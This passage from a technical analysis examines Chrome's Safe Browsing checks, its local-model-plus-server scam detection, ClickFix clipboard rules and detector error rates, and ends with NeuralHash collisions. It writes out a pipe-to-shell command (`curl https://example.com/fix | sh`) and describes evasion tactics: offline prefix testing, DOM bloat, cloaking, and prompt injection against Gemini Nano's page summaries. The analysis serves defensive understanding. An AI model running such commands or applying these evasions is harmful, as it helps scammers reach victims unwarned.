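2. It looks for the full hashes in the Global Cache. If it finds one, it doesn't make a real-time query, but it still checks the address against the threat lists on the device.
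3. Otherwise, it looks in a local cache of recent server responses. A full hash stored there that matches the address and hasn't expired leads straight to a warning.
4. It sends the remaining four-byte prefixes to the server, with no more than 30 in one request.
5. The server returns the full hashes that begin with those prefixes, together with the type of threat and an expiry time. The browser stores them and compares them with its own. A match means the address is unsafe, and no match means it is safe.

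Google's *Overview* of the API describes this as a change from allowing by default to checking by default. The browser used to send an address to the server only if it resembled an entry on a list of bad sites, but now it sends any address that doesn't match a list of good ones. The server receives far more queries, but it can catch a site that was added to its list a few seconds ago.

The Global Cache, a list of sites that are probably safe, contains full 32-byte hashes, unlike the threat lists. An accidental match with a threat list only causes an extra query, but an accidental match with the cache would let a phishing page skip the real-time check. If the cache used four-byte prefixes, a scammer could search for an address whose prefix matched. Google also has to choose the entries carefully, because if the cache listed an entire web-hosting service, every page on that service would get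 only the older, slower protection.

Checking an address over the network takes longer than looking it up in memory. *Safe Browsing*, a document from Chromium, the open-source project on which Chrome is built, describes an older design that checked every address before any content could load. In 2024 Google was introducing a way to let pages load during the real-time check. This makes browsing smoother, but a user may see the page briefly before the warning appears.

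If several queries in a row fail, Chrome goes back to the list on the device for a while. It does the same if a company's firewall blocks the relay that Google uses to hide users' network addresses. Someone who controls the network can therefore force Chrome to use an older list.

A complete loss of contact with the server has a worse effect. A prefix hit in the local list still needs a full-hash request, and under Google's *Local List Mode*, the program should treat the address as safe if that request fails. A site that has been on the list for weeks would then open without a warning, unless the browser had stored a recent server response. Warning about every hit during an outage would prevent this, but nearly all of those warnings would be wrong. Most phishers don't control their victims' networks, so treating the address as safe is a reasonable choice here. It would be riskier in a system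 where the person being checked owns the device and can cut its connection.

### The modes available in 2026

Google's *How To Guides* list three modes for version 5 of the API. The third is for programs that can't store lists or are designed not to, and Google's *No Storage Real Time Mode* gives its procedure.

| Mode | Stored on the device | When the device asks the server | If the server can't be reached |
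|---|---|---|---|
| Real-time | Global Cache, threat lists and recent responses | When the address is not in the Global Cache, or has a prefix hit on a threat list | Uses the threat lists on the device |
| Local list | Threat lists and recent responses | Only after a prefix hit | Treats the address as safe |
| No-storage real-time | Recent responses only | For every address that recent responses don't settle | Treats the address as safe |

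A program can also send Google the complete address instead of hash prefixes. This is simpler to build, but it shows Google exactly what the user is visiting. For programs that send prefixes, the API accepts only four-byte prefixes, because longer ones would reveal more about the address.

Chrome's Standard protection checks web addresses in real time, but Google was still developing these checks for Incognito and Guest modes in November 2026 (Ofonagoro, 2026, *Google Plans Chrome Incognito Safe Browsing Security Fix*). Firefox moved to version 5 of Safe Browsing with Firefox 147, released on 13 January (Brinkmann, 2026). Mozilla's bug tracker entry *Enable SafeBrowsing V5* covers both desktop and Android.

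Firefox uses local list mode. Google's guide lists missed protection as a drawback of this mode, because the list is only as current as its last update. This contradicts CyberInsider's *Firefox 147 tightens web security reduces data sharing with Google*, which describes the result as near real-time protection. A browser can adopt version 5 and still have the delay that led Google to change Chrome.

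### What an attacker can learn from each list

A scammer can download the threat lists after every update and search them for the prefixes of their own addresses. The test is free, and Google can't see it. If the prefixes are missing, no browser using that version of the list will warn about the site. If one is present, Google has almost certainly found the site, since each string has only about a 1 in 1,400 chance of matching by accident. Someone running hundreds of phishing pages could automatically abandon each one as it was listed.

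A scammer can test an address against the server's list by opening the page in Chrome to see whether a warning appears, or by querying the API, which requires a key and counts against a quota. The server's response is more reliable than the offline test because it contains full hashes. Anyone can therefore still use the server list to check an address they already know, but each uncached test now sends a request to Google.

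Copying the entire list is harder. At 30 prefixes per request, checking all 2³² possible prefixes would take about 143 million requests. Someone who starts from 3 million downloaded prefixes needs only about 100,000 requests, but would miss the newest entries, which matter most to a scammer. Either way, the copier gets only hashes, so they can test guessed addresses but can't read the listed ones directly.

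Google still distributes threat lists, so scammers can still test their addresses offline for free. The results are now less useful, because an address missing from the downloaded list may already be on the server's list. Scammers can no longer count on having 30 to 60 minutes between Google identifying a site and Chrome detecting it.

A scammer can learn little from either list about how Google finds the sites it lists. Each response shows only whether one exact address is listed, without a score that the scammer could try to improve step by step. A scammer may learn more by probing a trained model, because the result for one item may help predict the result for a similar one.

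Downloaded lists also let outsiders check on the operator. Gerbet and colleagues compared prefixes on the lists with the full hashes that the servers returned, and found that some prefixes had no matching full hash. These entries can't produce a warning, but they still make browsers contact the server. Researchers would find it much harder to look for such entries in a list that stays on the server.

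### Sites that nobody has found

Moving the list to the server removes most of the delay between listing a site and protecting users from it, but it doesn't reduce the time Google needs to find the site. Google acknowledged in 2024 that real-time checks in Standard protection cover only sites it has already confirmed to be unsafe. That leaves out very new sites and those that show Google's crawlers a harmless version. By the migration guide's estimate, out-of-date lists accounted for at most 30% of missed phishing protection.

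Chrome's optional Enhanced Protection sends Google more data and uses machine learning to look for unlisted sites. Li (2026), in *Google says Chrome’s Safe Browsing Enhanced Protection mode makes users 10x safer*, reports Google's claim that it makes users ten times safer than Standard protection. But Hesse (2026), in *Google Chrome verbessert Schutz vor Phishing und Online-Betrug*, points out that the figure compares the average number of warnings shown, not the number of attacks prevented. Some of the extra warnings may be mistaken, and people who choose Enhanced Protection may visit different sites. The figure is still evidence that lists alone miss a great deal. Chrome also runs an on-device model that examines the page itself to find phishing pages that aren't on any list.

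## Letting a browser model flag pages and a server decide

Chrome uses two small models, downloaded from Google, to find phishing pages that nobody has listed yet. The content model examines the page's address, its wording and its DOM, the tree of forms, links, images and other elements that make up the page. The visual model examines how the page looks. If either model scores the page above its threshold, Chrome sends data about the page to Safe Browsing's servers, which decide whether the user sees a warning.

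Pourmohamad, Wirsz and colleagues (2024), in *Deep Dive into Client-Side Anti-Phishing*, traced this system through Chrome's source code from version 79 to 108. They found that the browser periodically downloads both models and their thresholds. Google can therefore retrain a model or change a threshold without releasing a new version of Chrome, but attackers can get the new model as soon as users do.

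### Scores and thresholds

The content model gives one score for the whole page. The visual model gives a score for each of several categories, and each category has its own threshold.

Hoang Nguyen Dai built a copy of Chromium and used it to open an imitation of Bank of America's site. The content score passed its threshold, but none of the visual scores did, even though the imitation had the bank's logo and layout. Imitations of Chase's and Wells Fargo's sites gave the same result. Daniel Rubery, who answered Hoang's questions on the developers' mailing list, did not know what the visual categories represent. Hoang tested too few pages to measure the visual model's accuracy, but the results show that it can miss a close copy of a bank's site.

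Hoang also wrote a small function to read out the thresholds. An attacker can do the same and then see how far a page's score is from triggering a flag. Getting the models may take extra work, because another developer on the list reported that Google's server would not send them to a home-built browser.

### Who decides on the warning

According to Rubery, Chrome sends data about a flagged page to Safe Browsing for a more demanding analysis, and warns the user only if Safe Browsing finds that the page is phishing. Pourmohamad and colleagues instead write that Chrome shows a warning as soon as any score passes its threshold, and reports the page to Google at the same time. The server then decides only whether to add the address to the blocklist that protects other users. When Hoang asked whether a similar description in academic papers was correct, Rubery replied that it was not.

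Chromium's source code supports Rubery's account. The file that controls this process (Chromium, 2020) has a 2020 copyright date but also covers much newer features. After the model flags a page, the browser sends a request to Google and names a function to run when the reply arrives. This function is the only part of the file that displays a warning, and it does so only if the server has classified the page as phishing or a scam. If the user has already moved to another page, the browser still sends the request but shows no warning.

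If Chrome has stored a recent verdict for a page's address, it can also warn about the page without sending a new request or running the models again.

The study ended with version 108, so we can't tell from the newer code how every earlier version behaved. But the two designs would look much the same to someone watching the screen, because in both, a warning covers the page soon after it gets a high score.

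If the local score alone could trigger a warning, anyone who could push a harmless page's score over the threshold could make Chrome warn people away from it. The server check makes this harder, but if the server doesn't reply, a phishing page opens without a warning even when its local score is very high.

### Checks before the models run

Most pages never reach the models. When a page loads, Chromium's code goes through these checks first:

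1. It skips anything that isn't an ordinary web page, such as Chrome's own settings pages, files in other formats, and pages from the user's own computer or a private network.
2. It skips Incognito tabs and any site that a company has exempted for its employees.
3. It looks for the address on an allowlist made for this feature. A match ends the process, with very rare random exceptions.
4. It looks for the address on a second allowlist of sites that Google is highly confident about. A match here ends the process 9,999 times out of 10,000.
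5. It looks for a stored verdict and uses that if there is one.
6. It stops if the browser has reached its limit on the number of reports it may send.

The allowlists do most of the filtering. According to a comment in the code, pages match the first allowlist about 1,000 times as often as the local models trigger a request. Skipping allowlisted pages saves computing power and prevents many false flags, but it also means the models will almost never check a phishing page on an allowlisted site. The Global Cache creates a similar risk for address checks.

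The limit on reports protects Google's servers from a browser that flags everything. But once a browser reaches its limit, it stops looking for new phishing pages this way, although users can still report a page themselves.

### What Chrome sends

When a local model flags a page, Chrome sends Google the page's address and the models' scores, and may add a blurred image of the page. For people who use Enhanced Protection, it can also add an image embedding, a list of numbers that another local model computes from the page's appearance. Pages that look alike get similar lists. These users' requests also include the chain of pages that led them there and, if they are signed in, a token for their Google account. Chrome sends Google a full-size screenshot only when the user chooses to report the page.

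This is much more than the four-byte hash prefixes that Chrome sends when it checks an address. The user therefore loses some privacy when the local models wrongly flag a page, even if the server rejects the flag and no warning appears.

The image embedding may also have a second use. The code includes a study, limited to Enhanced Protection users, in which the browser compares a page's embedding with a set of target embeddings. This resembles matching a photo against a list of perceptual hashes, except that a match only sends the page to the server.

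### Requests that don't need a flag from the models

Hoang's last question to Rubery was whether Chrome requests a server classification only when a page scores high. Nobody on the list answered. In the code, several other conditions also trigger a request, most of them only under Enhanced Protection.

| Reason for the request | What happens on the device |
|---|---|
| A phishing model | A score passes its threshold |
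| A suspicious address | Safe Browsing's reply to an address check asks for a report on the page, or on an address that redirected to it |
| The page's behaviour | The page asks to send notifications, locks the keyboard or makes the phone vibrate, for example |
| A payment form | The user selects a credit card field, although settings can limit this to unfamiliar sites or, on Android, to links opened from a text message app |
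| Copied text | The user copies text from the page, and its length is within set limits |
| A random sample | Chrome selects the page by chance |
| A user report | The user reports the page as unsafe |

When the page's behaviour causes the request, one setting lets Chrome skip the phishing models and send a score of zero. The local stage is then a simple rule instead of a trained model. An attacker can avoid triggering the rule by not using the feature it checks for, but the scam may not work without that feature.

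Requests about suspicious addresses are harder for an attacker to avoid. The server has already detected something wrong with the address and prompts the browser to examine the page more closely. Neither allowlist stops such a request, and Chrome sends it even if both models give the page a low score. A bad domain or a suspicious redirect can therefore trigger a server check even if a scammer has tested the page against the local models until it passes.

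Random samples give Google some information about pages that its local models didn't flag. A comment in the code gives the sampling rate as one in 100,000, but the value the software uses is 0.000001, or one in a million. If a billion people each opened 50 pages a day, this would produce at most 50,000 samples a day. If one page in 100,000 were phishing, the samples would include an average of one phishing page every two days. That is too few to measure how many phishing pages the local models miss, so Google would have to rely on other evidence, such as user reports.

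### How well the local models worked from 2019 to 2023

Pourmohamad and colleagues tested several versions of the classifier on real pages from PhishTank, a public collection of reported phishing sites, and report a detection rate of only 14%. Because the server must confirm each flag, warnings that depended on these flags could have reached at most 14% of the pages.

The researchers confirmed that a page could escape detection without lowering its score if it contained an excessive number of DOM elements. In one experiment, 34% of a set of known phishing sites bypassed the classifier. The current code has a related weakness. If the classifier starts but fails, for instance because it can't extract the page's features, Chrome normally sends nothing, just as it does when a page passes. A designer could count each failure as a flag instead, but would then have to handle more requests.

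The researchers also tested whether local detection helped other users by getting phishing sites onto Google's blocklist. They set up 14 groups of 35 artificial phishing sites and monitored each for seven days. In May 2020, local detection made little difference, and Google mainly listed sites that someone had reported to it. A second experiment in January 2021 had the same result. When the researchers told the Chrome team the following month, the team agreed and said it was working on improvements.

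By April 2023 Chrome had added the visual model, and the results were better. Google listed 10% of uncloaked sites with login forms within an hour and 51% within seven days. But it listed almost none of the cloaked sites, which use evasion techniques such as showing crawlers a harmless page. The local models also consistently missed pages without a login form, which suggests that they depended too much on that feature.

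These percentages are approximate, because in a group of 35 sites, each site counts for almost three percentage points. They also measure how quickly Google protected other people, not whether the first visitor saw a warning. Still, listing one site in ten within an hour is slow, because most malicious sites don't last long.

The result for cloaked sites is more surprising, since the browser receives the real page and so should be especially useful against cloaking. This may be because Google wanted its own crawler to confirm the page before listing it. If so, the second stage removed the main advantage of the first. The experiments predate default real-time address checks and Chrome's use of language models, so they are weak evidence of how well the system works now.

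### Gemini Nano on the device

Tech support scams usually don't need a login form. The page shows a fake virus warning to frighten the user into paying for help or giving the scammer remote access. It may also fill the whole screen and disable the keyboard and mouse.

In May 2025 Google added a check for these scams that uses Gemini Nano, a language model small enough to run on the user's computer. Bawa and colleagues describe the design, and Chromium's code adds some details:

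1. The page does something typical of a tech support scam, such as using the keyboard lock API, a browser function that lets a page capture keys that would normally control the browser or the operating system.
2. Chrome extracts the page's text, unless the site is on the high-confidence allowlist. It goes no further with the language model if the text is five bytes or shorter.
3. Gemini Nano reads the text and identifies the brand that the page claims to represent and the page's intent.
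4. Chrome sends these findings to Safe Browsing with the rest of its request.
5. Safe Browsing combines them with what it knows about the site and reaches a verdict. If it decides that the page is probably a scam, Chrome shows a warning.

Google limited these reports to Enhanced Protection users. People with Standard protection benefit only indirectly, when Google adds the sites it finds to its blocklists.

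In this design, a page's behaviour triggers the flag, Gemini Nano prepares evidence, and the server decides. Running the model on every page would use too much of the computer's processing power, so Chrome runs it rarely and limits its use of the graphics processor. If the model isn't available on a device, Chrome still sends the request to the server and notes the reason.

Sending a summary protects privacy better than sending the page's text, but the scammer wrote the text being summarized. A page could include instructions for the model to describe it as a news article, an attack known as prompt injection. Bawa and colleagues say that Google was studying this problem along with "timing bypass", which presumably means hiding the scam until the analysis has finished. A scammer can also run Gemini Nano on their own computer and rewrite the page until the summary looks harmless. The server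 can still reject that summary because of the site's reputation, but a new site may not have one yet.

### Moving the language model to the server

In October 2026 Google moved this analysis to a Gemini model on its servers for Enhanced Protection users. Pogorelec (2026) reports in *Chrome flags malicious commands that scammers pass off as fixes* that the new version also looks for fake antivirus and browser update scams. The model assesses the brand, the page's intent and the likelihood of a scam. Safe Browsing still combines this analysis with the domain's reputation and other evidence to reach the verdict.

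Google says Chrome sends the page's text only when the site shows "high-confidence scam indicators". The local stage therefore determines which pages reach the stronger model. Google has not published a list of the indicators.

After the move, attackers no longer have a private copy of the model that produces the summary. To find out how the new model will describe a page, they have to submit the page to Google, which can count and limit such attempts. They can still study the indicators offline if the software that detects them runs on the device.

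In Chromium's code for the server-side scan, the browser receives the brand and intent that the model found, then adds them to its request to Safe Browsing. If the released feature works this way, someone with a modified browser could read the model's findings for their own page and learn more than they would from seeing whether a warning appeared. The same source file also starts a separate Gemini anti-scam service, so the released feature may work differently.

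The drawback for users is that Google can now receive the text of a page, not just a summary. That text could include private information if a harmless page happens to show the indicators. *Chrome can now share your clipboard data with Google servers* (Gangwar, 2026) reports Google's statement that it never logs or keeps the text and doesn't use it to train AI. Users have to trust Google on this, whereas in the 2025 design the model read the text on their own computer.

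### Checking copied commands

Google announced a check for ClickFix scams at the same time. A ClickFix page displays a fake error and tells the user to fix it by copying a command and running it on their computer. The command then downloads malware outside the browser, where Chrome's download checks can't stop it. The copied command may also differ from the one the user sees on the page.

The local stage in Chromium's code is a set of rules. It splits the copied text into words and looks for a program that can download files, an address to download from, and something that can run the result. If it finds all three, it marks the text as suspicious.

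Suppose the copied text is `curl https://example.com/fix | sh`. `curl` downloads the file at the address, and `sh` runs its contents as commands. If both program names are on Chrome's lists, the rule treats the text as suspicious. But many legitimate software projects tell people to install their programs with this kind of command. The rule can't distinguish these commands from malicious ones, so the server has to, perhaps by using the address's reputation.

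The rules are also loose in other ways. For example, a closing bracket anywhere in the text counts as a sign that the text can run a command, because brackets can enclose one. Rules this loose work only because the server checks the result.

If the text isn't flagged as suspicious, Chrome's request can include the text's length, its word count and any words on Chrome's lists, but not the web addresses in it. If the text is flagged, the request includes the addresses and, if one setting is on, the full text. Gangwar and Pogorelec both report that Chrome removes personally identifiable information before it sends clipboard contents. The Chromium function that adds the full text doesn't do this, so the removal must happen elsewhere or in a different version of the code.

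### Two levels of warning

Until October 2026, the server's decision led to either a full-page red warning or no warning. Enhanced Protection now also shows a milder warning for sites that Google calls suspicious, which its announcement describes as having a "lower confidence verdict, possible risk of user harm" (quoted in Rijo, 2026, *Chrome adds suspicious-site warnings for 1 billion Enhanced Protection users*). The red warning remains for dangerous sites, where both Google's confidence and the risk of harm are high.

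A suspicious site triggers a pop-up, and Gangwar explains that the user can then go back to a safe page or mark the site as safe. Google says this milder design lets it show more warnings without undue risk.

As an invented example, suppose the server is very confident about 100 flagged pages, of which 98 are scams, and less sure about another 200, of which 140 are scams. If Google can only show red warnings, it may decide to leave those 200 pages alone, because 60 of the warnings would be wrong. With a pop-up, it can alert people to the 140 extra scams, and visitors to the 60 harmless pages get a small interruption instead of a blocked page. However, the pop-up will stop fewer people from entering a scam site than a red screen would.

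Rijo notes that Google has not said where it draws the line between the two levels, which patterns make a site suspicious or how many more warnings it expects to show. It also hasn't explained how the owner of a harmless site would find out about a pop-up or get it removed. A sales page with a countdown timer and buttons that imitate system messages might look enough like a scam to trigger a pop-up.

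## Calculating the error rates of the combined check

Chrome's server and Apple's second hash examine only what the device has already passed on, and this order determines how the errors of the two stages combine. An item gets a bad verdict only if the local model flags it and the server confirms the flag. The probability of both is the probability of a flag multiplied by the probability that the server confirms a flagged item. Working this out separately for harmless and bad items gives two rules:

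- Combined false positive rate = local false positive rate × the server's false positive rate on harmless items that the local model flagged
- Combined recall = local recall × the server's recall on bad items that the local model flagged

The rules hold for any pair of models, even two copies of the same one, as long as the server's rates are measured on items the local model flagged. The server's recall on those items can't exceed 100%, so the combined recall can't exceed the local model's. Confirmation can remove false alarms, but it can also add misses by rejecting items the local model flagged correctly.

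### A million items

Suppose 1,000 of 1,000,000 items are bad. The local model has a recall of 95% and a false positive rate of 1%. On the items it flags, the server has a recall of 98% and a false positive rate of 1%.

| Stage | Bad items | Harmless items | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Before any check | 1,000 | 999,000 | | |
| Flagged by the local model | 950 | 9,990 | 8.7% | 95% |
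| Confirmed by the server | 931 | about 100 | about 90% | 93.1% |

Of the 69 bad items that escape detection, the local model missed 50 and the server failed to confirm 19, so a perfect server would catch only 19 more.

The combined false positive rate is 0.01%, but one in ten confirmed flags is wrong because harmless items outnumber bad ones by 999 to 1. If only 100 of the million items were bad, the same two models would confirm about 93 flags correctly and 100 mistakenly. Precision would then be 48%, so a precision figure is hard to interpret without knowing the share of bad items in the traffic.

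Both stages also have to judge the same unit of content. *Cascade Detector Analysis and Application to Biomedical Microscopy* (2025) analyses a detector that scans coarse blocks of an image and then re-examines the flagged blocks in finer pieces. A harmless piece can reach the second stage because the first stage correctly flagged the block around it. The same would happen if a local model flagged whole conversations and the server judged single messages. With the rates above, a harmless message in a bad conversation would have a 0.95% chance (95% × 1%) of being wrongly confirmed, rather than 0.01%.

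### Loosening the local threshold

A designer can reduce misses by lowering the score at which the local model flags an item. The table uses invented but plausible rates for a stricter and a looser local threshold, and keeps the server's rates at 98% and 1%.

| Local threshold | Local recall | Local false positive rate | Items sent to the server | Correct verdicts | Mistaken verdicts | Precision | Combined recall |
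|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Strict | 85% | 0.2% | 2,848 | 833 | 20 | 98% | 83.3% |
| As above | 95% | 1% | 10,940 | 931 | 100 | 90% | 93.1% |
| Loose | 99% | 5% | 50,940 | 970 | 500 | 66% | 97.0% |

Moving from the middle row's threshold to the loose one catches 39 more bad items. It also sends the server 40,000 more items, nearly all of them harmless, and causes 400 more mistaken verdicts. The server's workload depends almost entirely on the local false positive rate, since even a perfect local model would send only 1,000 items.

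The designer could make the server stricter to compensate. If its false positive rate on flagged items fell to 0.2%, the loose setting would again produce about 100 mistaken verdicts. But a stricter server would also miss more bad items. If its recall fell below 94%, the system would catch fewer than the original 931, despite the extra traffic.

In practice, the server's rates would change with the local threshold. The local model scored the newly flagged harmless items as less suspicious, so the server may reject them more easily. If it wrongly confirmed only 0.3% of them, the loose setting would give about 220 mistaken verdicts instead of 500. The newly flagged bad items may also be harder to recognise. The operator therefore has to measure the server's rates again after every change to the local threshold.

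### Why the server's rate must come from flagged items

An operator might instead test the server on a random sample of harmless items, find a false positive rate of 1%, and multiply it by the local model's 1%. This is correct only if the two models make mistakes independently. *Aggregating multiple test results to improve medical decision-making* notes that researchers commonly assume medical tests are independent because this simplifies the mathematics and manufacturers typically don't report how their tests depend on each other.

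Two content detectors are unlikely to make independent errors. Both may wrongly flag a harmless page that copies the layout of a bank's login screen, while neither flags a recipe page. The harmless items that the local model sends to the server are therefore the hardest ones to classify.

The size of the effect depends on the correlation ρ between the two models' mistakes on harmless items. It is 0 if the mistakes are independent and, when both models have the same error rate, 1 if they always coincide. If *f*₁ and *f*₂ are the two false positive rates on all harmless items, the share that both models get wrong is

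*f*₁*f*₂ + ρ√(*f*₁(1 − *f*₁)*f*₂(1 − *f*₂))

With both rates at 1%, the first term is 0.01% and the second is 0.99% × ρ, so even a weak correlation, anything above about 0.01, makes the second term larger than the first. The next table applies the formula to the million items, with the number of correct verdicts fixed at 931.

| Correlation ρ | Server's false positive rate on flagged items | Mistaken verdicts | Precision |
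|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 1% | 100 | 90% |
| 0.1 | 10.9% | 1,089 | 46% |
| 0.3 | 30.7% | 3,067 | 23% |
| 1 | 100% | 9,990 | 9% |

An operator who multiplied the separate rates would expect 100 mistaken verdicts in every row.

*A review of methods for the analysis of diagnostic tests* (Fanshawe, Nicholson and colleagues, 2024) gives a real case in which patients took the same stool test for bowel cancer twice. Of 1,299 people without cancer, 129 tested positive the first time and 111 the second. If the errors were independent, about 11 people would have had two false positives, but 63 did. The second test had a false positive rate of 8.5% overall and 49% among people who had already tested positive. Repeating the same test is close to the worst case, comparable to running a slightly larger version of the local model on the server.

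Correlation between the two checks can also improve the combined recall. *Two-test algorithms for infectious disease diagnosis* explains that when two tests are positively correlated, the second has a higher sensitivity (the medical term for recall) among people who tested positive on the first. Likewise, the bad items that reach a server are the easier ones to detect, so its recall on them may be higher than on bad items in general. This raises the combined recall above the product of the two separate recalls, but never above the local model's recall.

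Viola and Jones dealt with the problem in their face detector, a chain of classifiers, by training each classifier on image regions that had passed all the previous ones, as *Exploring and Exploiting Diversity for Image Segmentation* (2017) describes. *Robust Real-time Extraction of Fiducial Facial Feature Points using Haar-like Features* (2015) gives an example with 15 stages, each of which keeps at least 99.5% of faces and lets through at most half of everything else. The whole chain lets through about 3 in 100,000 other regions, but the losses of 0.5% of faces at each stage add up to about 7%. Multiplying the stages' rates to get these totals is valid if each stage meets its targets on the regions that reach it.

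### Whether different models make different mistakes

Evidence from language models suggests that a server model may repeat many of the on-device model's mistakes, even if it comes from another company and has another architecture. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) compared more than 350 models. On one set of multiple-choice questions, when two models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time, against 33% for random guesses. Models from the same company agreed more, but so did more accurate models, even when they came from different companies. One model from Google and one from the company Writer, with no publicly known connection, gave the same answer on 99.87% of the questions that both got wrong.

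*Shared Item-Level Error Limits the Aggregation of Small Language Models* (2026) also reports shared errors. When 15 models made rough numerical estimates, the average correlation between their errors was 0.83, or about 0.65 with methods that limit the influence of extreme cases. Models from the same family did not make noticeably more similar errors than other models, contrary to what Kim and colleagues found. Errors in the answer key could explain part of the correlation, and items that people mislabelled in a detector's test set could have the same effect.

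*The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) reports correlations of 0.74 to 0.82 between the forecasting errors of models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google. Some of that correlation comes from the calculation itself, because the study subtracts the same outcome from every model's forecast.

None of these three studies tested content detectors, and the correlations they measured are not the ρ in the formula above. They are good evidence against assuming that ρ is zero, but they can't be used to set its value. *Quantifying Correlations of Machine Learning Models* (2025) is more relevant because it includes image and text classifiers, whose errors were also positively correlated. It found that models make similar errors when they share the features that best predict the outcome. This suggests giving the server information that the local model lacks. Chrome's server, for example, can use a site's reputation,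 which can't be judged from the page's appearance.

### Measuring the two stages in use

To measure the server's false positive rate, the operator can have people label a random sample of flagged items. In the running example, a sample of 1,000 flags would contain about 913 harmless items, of which the server would wrongly confirm about nine. An estimate based on nine cases is rough, and the true rate could plausibly be from 0.5% to 1.9%.

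The labels need to come from people, not from the server or another model. Kim and colleagues tested the common practice of using one language model to grade others. The grader marked a wrong answer as correct whenever it made the same mistake, so it overrated weaker models, especially those from its own company. An operator who scored the local model against the server's verdicts would overestimate the local model's precision for the same reason.

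Local recall is much harder to measure because nobody examines the items that the local model doesn't flag. Medical statisticians call this partial verification. In the example, an operator who checked only flagged items would see that the server confirmed 931 of 950 bad ones and might report a recall of 98%, when the combined check's true recall is 93.1%. The local model missed 50 bad items among 989,060 unflagged ones, so a random sample of 100,000 unflagged items would contain about five. Test collections of known bad items take less work, but they may not resemble the bad items in current traffic.

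All of these rates describe ordinary traffic. Someone who deliberately alters items can change either stage's rate.

### The library size that Apple's threshold allows

Apple's design adds another step to the calculation, because a false match has no consequence until the account has enough of them. If false matches are rare and independent, their number in a library follows a Poisson distribution, which needs only the average. For *n* photos and a false-match rate of *p* per photo, the average is λ = *np*, and the probability of at least 30 false matches is

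P(at least 30) = 1 − Σ e^(−λ) λ^*k* / *k*!, with the sum running from *k* = 0 to 29

At Apple's assumed rate of one in a million, this probability stays below one in a trillion for libraries of up to about 5.77 million photos (λ ≈ 5.77). If the server can open the records only at the 31st match, as the protocol paper implies, the limit is 6.17 million. Both limits are consistent with Apple's assumption of a library larger than any in existence.

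The limit is inversely proportional to the false-match rate:

| False matches per photo | Largest library for which 30 matches stay below one in a trillion |
|---|---|
| 3 in 100 million (Apple's measurement) | 192 million photos |
| 1 in 1 million (Apple's assumption) | 5.77 million |
| 1 in 100,000 | 577,000 |
| 1 in 10,000 | 57,700 |

The threshold therefore protects everyone only if the assumed rate holds for each person's photos, but Apple measured an average. In *Revisiting First Impressions*, a blog post on Apple's figures, Lewis objected that nobody outside the company knew what kinds of photos it had tested or how long the list was. Both matter because the hash might work differently on some kinds of image, and a longer list gives each photo more chances to match.

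Before Apple published these figures, Lewis's *Obfuscated Apples* inferred a false-match rate of about one in 2,900 from the one-in-a-trillion promise, assuming a threshold of ten and an account that adds three or four photos a day. At that rate, a new parent taking 50 photos a day would have had a 6% chance of passing the threshold within a year. Apple's later figures replaced those assumptions, but the example shows why a single threshold has to suit the heaviest users.

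The calculation also assumes that one false match doesn't make another more likely. If matches are independent, an innocent library of 50,000 photos has a less than one in 10^71 chance of reaching 30 false matches at Apple's assumed rate. If the library instead consists of 5,000 bursts of ten nearly identical shots, and every shot in a burst gets the same hash, the average rate is unchanged but three falsely matching bursts are enough to reach 30. The probability of that is about one in 48 million, or roughly 20,000 times Apple's target.

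Bhowmick and colleagues don't describe the mechanism meant to handle duplicate photos, so nobody outside Apple can calculate how much of this risk would have remained.

### Unaltered photos with the same hash

Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel tested how evenly NeuralHash spreads different images over its possible hashes. They extracted the function from an iPhone and ran it on 202,599 celebrity photos from the public CelebA collection. They also ran it on versions of those photos blurred by different amounts, and on a set of pictures without people. When two images had the same hash, they looked at both and counted a false collision only if the images were clearly different.

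If all 2⁹⁶ codes of a 96-bit hash were equally likely, the first collision between any two images would come after about 2⁴⁸ (280 trillion) hashes. With images of faces, it came after about 2¹⁶ (66,000) hashes.

The researchers also tested PhotoDNA, using leaked code that they could run but not inspect. PhotoDNA's codes are 1,152 bits long, and two codes can match without being identical. Microsoft hasn't disclosed how close they must be, so the researchers tried distance limits of 150 and 175, the ends of a range that earlier research had recommended.

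| Function and images | False collisions | Hashes before the first one | Similar images missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| NeuralHash, pictures without people | 0 | None found | Not reported |
| NeuralHash, faces | 12 | 2^16.1 (about 70,000) | 64.7% |
| NeuralHash, heavily blurred faces | 270 | 2^11.6 (about 3,100) | 47.3% |
| PhotoDNA, faces, limit of 150 | 1 | 2^17 (about 131,000) | 24.1% |
| PhotoDNA, faces, limit of 175 | 32 | 2^14.6 (about 25,000) | 17.8% |

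Collisions come early because some digits of the hash are biased and some help to predict others. In a well-spread hash, each digit is 1 about half the time. For faces, 30 of NeuralHash's 96 digits were 1 less than 35% or more than 65% of the time. That bias alone would lower the number of hashes expected before the first collision from 2^48 to 2^43.5. The researchers estimate that, for faces, NeuralHash collides about as often as an ideal hash of only 31 bits.

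Roboflow's *neuralhash collisions* (2021) reported two exact NeuralHash collisions between unaltered images in ImageNet, a large public image collection. Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel later described their own work as the first to find such collisions, but its main contribution is to show how strongly the collision rate depends on the type of image.

Apple told the researchers that it had reproduced all their results. It acknowledged the issues and said it was investigating solutions. Microsoft began discussions with the researchers, who say their PhotoDNA results are accurate for the version now in use.

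### How far the collisions undermine Apple's calculation

The 2¹⁶ figure counts hashes until *any* two images in a growing collection collide. It doesn't mean that one face photo in 65,000 would match Apple's list, because a collection of 70,000 images contains about 2.5 billion pairs that could collide. The study's false positive rates are likewise the share of images that collide with any other image in the set, so they rise with the size of the set, to an estimated 5.5% for 100 million unblurred faces. The researchers compare these rates with a requirement that a system wrongly identify no more than one image in 50 billion as abuse material, but the two figures aren't directly comparable because the requirement concerns matches with a list.

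A fairer comparison uses the collision rate per pair of faces, which was 12 in 20.5 billion, or about one in 1.7 billion. At that rate, about one in 17,000 new portraits would falsely match a hypothetical list of 100,000 similar portraits, which is nearly 60 times Apple's assumed rate. A threshold of 30 matches would then keep the risk of wrongly flagging an account below one in a trillion only for libraries of up to about 99,000 photos.

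This test is unfavourable to Apple because CelebA consists mostly of front-facing portraits, unlike a typical photo library or the abuse list. The researchers had asked organisations that hold abuse images for a way to test on real material, but had received no positive reply by the time they submitted the paper. Apple's measurement of three matches in 100 million used the real list, so it remains better evidence about the average photo. But the face results are evidence that the average error rate can be far too low for someone whose photos all resemble one another.

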